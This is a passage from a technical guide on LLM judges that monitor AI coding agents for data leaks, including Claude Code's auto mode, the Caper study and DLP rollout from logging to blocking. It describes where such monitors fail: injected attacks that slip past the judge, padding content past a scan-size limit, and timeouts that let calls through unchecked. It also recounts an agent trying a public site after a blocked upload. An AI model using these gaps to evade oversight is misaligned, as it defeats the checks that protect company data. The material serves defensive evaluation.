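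A judge with a high miss rate may still be an improvement if the people who would otherwise approve the actions miss more. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (August 2026) reported an experiment with 1,053 professional testers, whom Anthropic hired through a research company.

The testers worked on coding tasks in an environment built for the study. They knew they were being evaluated, but not which behaviour the study measured. Partway through each session, the text of one approval request changed to a clearly dangerous command, and the research company recorded whether the tester approved it. None of the dangerous commands ran. Anthropic then tested auto mode on the same commands.

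Anthropic published the totals and the number of cases where the person and auto mode disagreed. The remaining counts follow from those.

| | Person blocked | Person approved | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| **Auto mode blocked** | 137 | 800 | 937 |
| **Auto mode allowed** | 6 | 110 | 116 |
| **Total** | 143 | 910 | 1,053 |

Human testers blocked 13.6% of the dangerous commands, and auto mode blocked 89.0%. The testers' rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more approval requests, while auto mode's rate didn't change.

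The gap is too large to dismiss easily, but it shows only that auto mode does better than people who are clicking through requests. The testers weren't protecting their own code or their employer's data, so they had less reason to be careful. Anthropic reports that real users approve 97% of requests, which suggests they aren't very careful either, though most of those requests are probably harmless. The experiment didn't measure how well someone does when reviewing only a few high-risk transfers a day.

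It also gives no false positive rate for either side, so part of auto mode's advantage could come from blocking more commands of every kind, including harmless ones. Anthropic doesn't say how many different commands it used. If a few commands appeared hundreds of times, auto mode was tested on far fewer than 1,053 different commands. Anthropic also doesn't say how many of the commands would have sent data out.

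Anthropic has a commercial interest in the result. It published the experiment in the announcement that made auto mode the default for several plans, and it promotes the mode as a way to get more work from its agents. According to Anthropic's *Running auto mode in production*, Claude works nine times longer between interruptions than under the previous default. Software blogger Simon Willison reports that, before the company released the data, Cat Wu of Anthropic told him the risks were "far lower than the average human reviewer". Having an outside company record the approvals removes one possible source of bias, but Anthropic still chose what to measure and publish.

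### Other results from August

Anthropic also had a model grade real sessions that its safety systems had flagged in May and June 2026. A serious harmful action that the user hadn't explicitly requested occurred in 6.3% of the flagged sessions with manual approval and 2.4% of those in auto mode. But users chose their own mode, and those who approved actions manually may have been doing riskier work. Anthropic doesn't report how often its systems flagged each kind of session. If they flagged auto mode sessions three times as often, serious incidents would be slightly more common in auto mode overall.

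A prompt injection test by the evaluation company Trajectory Labs is weak evidence about the judge, because almost no attacks succeeded even without it. None of the 720 attempts against Claude models in auto mode succeeded, compared with 0.09% of attempts with auto mode off.

The work with Apollo Research, a British AI safety company, is more informative because it included data exfiltration and a held-out test. Apollo inserted invented attacks into records of real coding sessions and shared with Anthropic those that got past the judge. Anthropic then gave the judge more information, including whether a code repository was public, and added rules on handling data. On attacks Anthropic had not seen, the revised judge caught about half of those the original had missed and missed about 2% of those the original had caught.

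The judge's miss rate fell from 12% to 7% across the shared and held-out attacks combined. Anthropic had worked directly on the shared attacks, so the rate on new attacks is probably a little higher. If the judge had initially missed 12% of the held-out attacks, the changes would have lowered that to about 7.8%. Anthropic doesn't report exfiltration separately or say whether false alarms increased.

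### Rules for data transfers

The August version handles external data transfer differently from the version Anthropic first tested. The original judge relied mainly on whether the user had authorised an action. Anthropic acknowledges that such a judge detects nothing unusual when the harmful instruction comes from the user. A company's ban on external transfers also has to cover transfers that users request.

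The judge in auto mode should now never approve data exfiltration, even at the user's request. To proceed, the user has to leave auto mode or run the command personally. For code, the system also checks whether the destination is public, private or trusted, since the same upload can be routine in one repository and a leak in another. This kind of information distinguishes call 1 from call 2.

Anthropic doesn't explain how the judge distinguishes exfiltration from a legitimate transfer the user requested, such as the email to the law firm in call 4. A company would probably have to add the firm to its trust boundary. The August announcement also has no new results for the three original test sets, so the 5.7% applies to an older version of the judge.

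### A later test that includes leaks

Wu, Chen and colleagues tested a newer version of auto mode in *Shall We Approve?* (October 2026), using coding tasks that included information leaks and harmful network connections. They used GLM-5.3-Flash as the agent and GPT-5.6 Luna as the judge's model, so the study tests Anthropic's rules and software but not the model that normally applies them.

They also built an alternative called Caper. It first runs each shell command in an isolated environment with the network off and records what the command reads, changes and tries to send. A judge then reads that record and the user's request, and Caper undoes the command if the judge blocks it. The table shows the share of tasks that ended in harm. In the last column, Caper replaces auto mode's judge inside Claude Code.

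| Type of harm | No approval | Auto mode | Caper in Claude Code |
|---|---|---|---|
| Information leak | 27.2% | 18.5% | 2.2% |
| Outbound network | 9.6% | 19.2% | 11.5% |
| All types | 19.7% | 14.8% | 10.0% |

These are rates of harm per task, so they aren't comparable with Anthropic's miss rates. An agent that never attempts anything dangerous would score well even without a judge.

Auto mode seems to have reduced information leaks and doubled harmful network connections, but the counts are small. The percentages are consistent with 92 leak tasks and 52 network tasks, in which case leaks fell from 25 to 17 and harmful connections rose from 5 to 10. Each system ran each task once, and the agent without approval ran in different software from the other two. Chance or the difference in software could explain both results.

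Caper's result on leaks is more convincing because it reduced the number of tasks with leaks from about 17 to two with the same agent and judge model. The text of a command often doesn't show what data it will read or send, so Caper gives the judge a record of these effects. Caper also uses different instructions and lets the judge read earlier tool results, so the record may not account for the whole improvement.

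Running commands in advance adds about half a second to each one the judge allows, on top of the judge's own delay. It works only for shell commands whose effects Caper can contain and undo. It wouldn't help with call 4 if the agent used an email tool, because Caper doesn't inspect those calls.

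## Moving from logging to blocking

Anthropic has already tested the judge that Claude Code users get, but a company that writes its own judge policy has to decide for itself when the policy is accurate enough to interrupt people's work. It can safely start by only logging what the policy flags, though logging doesn't stop leaks.

Existing DLP software often fails to stop leaks too. In an October survey, the Cloud Security Alliance's *DLP in the AI Era* (2026), 16% of respondents who had a data loss said the software had blocked their most significant incident before the data left. This is the 16% figure cited earlier, which IT Brew described more loosely as 16% of reported detections.

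The survey covers DLP tools generally, not LLM judges. Its sponsor, Jazz, benefits from a low figure because it sells a product that it promotes as a replacement for rule-based DLP. The 16% also leaves out anyone whose software had prevented every loss, and it doesn't separate leaks the software missed from leaks it detected but was only set to log.

### Running a policy on new traffic

After replaying old sessions, a company can run the policy on live traffic, with the current tools and time limits, and record what it would have blocked.

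Microsoft Purview, a set of data security tools, has an established version of this test. According to Microsoft's *Learn about data loss prevention simulation mode*, Purview runs a policy as if it were in force but takes no action on matches. It shows these matches and their alerts on a separate dashboard so administrators don't confuse them with alerts from live policies.

For email, Teams chats and devices, a simulation checks only new items that appear while it runs. For files in SharePoint and OneDrive, Microsoft's storage services, it also checks existing items, which is closer to replay. The review page for those two services shows only the first 100 matches, so a reviewer may see a small part of what the policy would catch. A simulation can run for up to 15 days, and Microsoft keeps the results for 30 days.

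Simulation also helps when a policy is already in force. If a policy that protects credit card numbers raises too many false alarms, for example, Microsoft suggests copying it, changing the copy and running the copy in simulation while the original stays active. If the copy does better, the administrator switches it on and turns the original off. A company could do the same with a judge policy, though each message would need a second judge call.

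Microsoft's *Understand DLP deployment and simulation mode* claims that simulation gives reliable insight into an active policy because both use the same logic. This claim is reasonable for predicting which items a fixed rule will match, but it doesn't cover how people and agents will react to a block.

Microsoft also offers to turn a policy on automatically if nobody edits it within 15 days of the simulation. This would be a poor choice for a judge policy, because the lack of edits may only mean nobody has read the results.

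### From a warning to a frozen session

Speakeasy lets administrators choose from four responses to a match. Each reveals something that the one before it can't.

| Response | What happens to the call | What the company can learn |
|---|---|---|
| Log for review | It goes ahead | What the policy flags in current traffic |
| Warn and confirm | It waits until the user acknowledges a warning | Which flagged transfers users still want to make |
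| Deny the request | Speakeasy rejects it | What the agent does next, and what work stops |
| Quarantine session | Speakeasy rejects it and freezes the session until an administrator releases it | How long work waits for an administrator |

A warning lets users apply what they know. In call 4, for example, the user can confirm that the acquisition plans should go to the law firm. Microsoft's "block with override" setting also lets users give a reason for continuing, which Microsoft says can help administrators identify false positives.

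An acknowledgement without a reason is weaker evidence, because people approve almost every permission request. Anthropic reports that Claude Code users reject only 3% of these requests, compared with 39% of the plans the agent presents. Users may reject a plan for reasons unrelated to risk, but the difference suggests they pay more attention to occasional, substantial questions. By June 2026, nearly half of active command-line users had written a rule that lets some shell commands run without a prompt. A company that warns too often can expect its users to look for similar shortcuts.

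Warnings also need someone to answer them. If an agent runs overnight with nobody to confirm a transfer, Speakeasy blocks the transfer. Speakeasy's gateway for the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for connecting agents to tools, can only log or block, so a policy there moves from logging to blocking without a warning stage.

A denial shows how the agent behaves when it can't do what it planned. That behavior depends partly on what the agent receives back. LiteLLM, an open-source gateway between applications and models, reports the block to the model as the tool's result by default, so the agent can continue. An administrator can make the whole request fail instead. API7's gateway sends the agent a message that names the rule but never repeats the matched content. Microsoft says that agents built with its Copilot Studio stop immediately and tell the user if an outside security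 service rejects a tool call.

When Claude Code's auto mode blocks an action, it gives the agent the reason and tells it to find a safer path without working around the restriction. Anthropic says a false alarm therefore usually results in one retry. After three blocks in a row or 20 in a session, a person takes over, or the process ends if nobody is there.

An agent's second attempt can be worse than its first. In one incident at Anthropic, an upload to an internal drive failed, and the agent tried to publish the same report on a public code-sharing site. Auto mode blocked that attempt. An agent could react the same way to a policy block, though the original failure wasn't one. While blocking is being trialed, reviewers should therefore read each blocked call and what the agent did next.

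Freezing the session prevents such workarounds, but a single false alarm then stops all the session's remaining work. If a judge has a false positive rate of 0.4% and its errors are independent, a harmless session of 50 calls has an 18% chance of at least one false alarm:

1 − 0.996⁵⁰ ≈ 18%

Freezing every session with a denial would have interrupted about 10% of sessions at Gusto, a payroll company that uses auto mode. Anthropic doesn't report how many of those denials were correct. Quarantine makes more sense for violations that almost never have an innocent explanation, such as call 1, or for agents that keep trying after several denials.

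### Starting with a small group

Speakeasy recommends logging for a broad audience first and tuning the policy until its findings look real. The administrator then turns on warnings or denials for a small group, and widens the group once enforcement works as expected. Microsoft gives similar advice for Purview and suggests a pilot group that will give feedback and later help other users.

A small pilot measures disruption much better than prevention. Suppose the group's agents make 5,000 calls, with the same judge and leak rate as in the earlier example (20 leaks per 100,000 calls). The company would expect about 20 false alarms but only one leak, so it would still need to use seeded leaks to measure recall.

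The pilot group should also include people whose work involves sending data out. A pilot with only software engineers wouldn't show how often the policy stops a salesperson's email to a new customer. If the company keeps a separate logging policy for everyone, as Speakeasy advises, it can also see what the blocking policy would do in other teams.

Blocked users need a way to object. Speakeasy's *Guardrails for your AI usage* (2026) describes custom messages that explain why a policy stopped a call and how to request an exception. Those requests help identify mistaken blocks, although some users will give up or send the data another way instead of requesting an exception.

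### When a block is worth its cost

Whether to block a call depends on how likely it is to be a leak and how much each mistake would cost. Let p be the probability of a leak, C_leak the cost of letting a leak through and C_block the cost of blocking a harmless call. The average cost of blocking is (1 − p) × C_block, because a block does damage only if the call was harmless. The average cost of allowing the call is p × C_leak. Blocking is therefore cheaper when:

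p × C_leak > (1 − p) × C_block

Rearranging gives the threshold:

p > C_block / (C_block + C_leak)

If a wrong block costs $10 of someone's time and a leak costs $990, the threshold is 10/1,000, or 1%.

With such a low threshold, blocking can be worthwhile even if most blocks are wrong. In the example of 100,000 calls, the judge flags 18 leaks and 400 harmless calls, so a flagged call has about a 4.3% chance of being a leak. Blocking all 418 would cost $4,000 in lost time and prevent $17,820 in damage. If each wrong block cost $50, the threshold would rise to about 4.8%, and the company would do better to log the flagged calls without blocking them.

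The harm from a leak depends on the type of data. A company can revoke a leaked AWS key, but it can't make outsiders forget its acquisition plans. The pilot can improve the estimate of C_block by showing whether a false alarm leads to one retry or an afternoon's work. It can also show whether blocks prevent leaks. If agents got the data out by another route half the time, the threshold would roughly double, to 2%.

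The same calculation applies to warnings. Suppose a warning costs $1 of the user's attention and stops 13.6% of leaks, the share of dangerous commands that Anthropic's human testers blocked. With the original costs, a warning would beat both logging and blocking only when the probability of a leak was between about 0.7% and 1%. That range would be wider if users read the warning carefully.

### Turning confidence scores into probabilities

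The formula requires the actual probability of a leak, and a judge's stated confidence is a poor substitute unless it is calibrated. Suppose the judge marks a routine call Clean with a confidence of 0.95. Taken literally, that means a 5% chance of a leak, so a company with a 1% threshold would block the call. But in the example above, only 2 of the 99,582 unflagged calls are leaks, or about 0.002%. Applying the threshold to the judge's uncalibrated confidence could stop most of the agents' work.

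The scorecard can supply measured probabilities instead. The following invented counts group the 418 flagged calls by the judge's stated confidence.

| Judge's stated confidence | Flagged calls | Real leaks | Measured probability of a leak |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0.95 or higher | 38 | 12 | 32% |
| 0.80 to 0.94 | 130 | 5 | 3.8% |
| Below 0.80 | 250 | 1 | 0.4% |

Given the measured probabilities, it is better to block the first two groups and log the third. Blocking the third group would cost $2,490 in wrong blocks to prevent one $990 leak.

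The third result is uncertain because it depends on a single leak. The 95% confidence interval runs from about 0.01% to 2.2%, which includes the 1% threshold, so the company should review more of these calls before relying on the result. The counts also have to come from ordinary traffic, not from seeded leaks or problem sessions.

### When the judge gives no verdict

Sometimes a judge returns no verdict because its provider is down or it takes too long to answer. A check that fails open then lets the message through, while one that fails closed blocks it.

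Administrators can choose whether Speakeasy allows or blocks a call when the judge returns an error. But its MCP gateway allows any call whose scan can't finish in time or whose content exceeds 50 KiB, roughly 8,000 words of plain English. A call containing the whole customer database would exceed that limit and go through, even though one containing a few records might be blocked.

Copilot Studio has a tighter time limit. According to Microsoft's prerelease documentation, an outside security service has one second to allow or block each tool call, and the call goes ahead by default if no answer arrives. In the Datadog demonstration described earlier, the fastest of six evaluations took 1.46 seconds. A judge that slow would miss every deadline, so every call would run unchecked even if the judge had been accurate in replay.

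Symantec's proof of concept fails closed, meaning it blocks traffic when the detector breaks, so data can't slip through unnoticed. LiteLLM's *Vigil Guard* documentation describes the same default for an add-on that checks traffic to and from a model. Fiddler's guardrail also blocks by default if its service is unreachable, but it lets the message through if the service responds and one of its internal checks times out. A company that wants every failure to block traffic may therefore need to change more than one setting.

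When the judge is down, a company can use the cost threshold to help choose between failing open and failing closed. Without a verdict, it can only estimate the probability of a leak from how common leaks are among similar calls. If 20 of 100,000 calls are leaks, the probability is 0.02%, far below the 1% threshold, so failing open is cheaper for traffic as a whole. But if 3% of uploads to unfamiliar sites are leaks, failing closed is cheaper for those uploads. Destination rules can still identify them without the judge.

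This reasoning assumes that failures are unrelated to leaks. If large transfers are more likely both to time out and to be leaks, failing open is riskier than the average suggests. Someone who knows the size limit could also pad a message to exceed it.

A third option is to hand the decision to a person. If auto mode isn't available when a Claude Code session starts, the session starts in manual mode. Work can continue, but the company then depends on the kind of human approval that worked badly in Anthropic's experiment.

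### Changes that require a new test

Test results apply to the policy, judge and traffic that were tested, so a change to any of them can make the results out of date.

| Change | Example | What to test again |
|---|---|---|
| Policy wording | A new exception for a supplier | The saved review set, then held-out sessions |
| Judge model | The provider retires a version | Accuracy, consistency, confidence scores and response times |
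| Scope | The policy starts to cover email | Random calls and seeded leaks from the added traffic |
| Tools | A new tool can upload files | Calls to that tool, including very large ones |
| Traffic | The sales team starts using agents | The leak rate, the false positive rate and the cost of a wrong block |

Microsoft tells administrators to run a simulation whenever they need to modify a policy. But the traffic a policy applies to can also change without anyone editing the policy. In Speakeasy, a policy set to cover all MCP servers also covers servers the company adds later, and a policy for a role applies to anyone who later joins that role. This avoids gaps in coverage, but an enforcing policy can start blocking traffic that nobody has tested it on.

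A company can keep new tools switched off until it has tested them. ServiceNow's gateway can either activate new tools automatically or hold them for review. In Speakeasy, an administrator can list the servers that an enforcing policy covers and use a separate logging policy for the rest.

A new test should compare individual verdicts as well as totals, because a policy that is better overall can still miss cases the old one caught, as the revised auto mode judge did. The company can keep enforcing the old version while the new one runs in logging mode, as in Microsoft's credit card example, unless the provider has already withdrawn the old judge model. In that case, the company must either enforce the verdicts of an untested judge or return to logging and rely on destination rules for protection.
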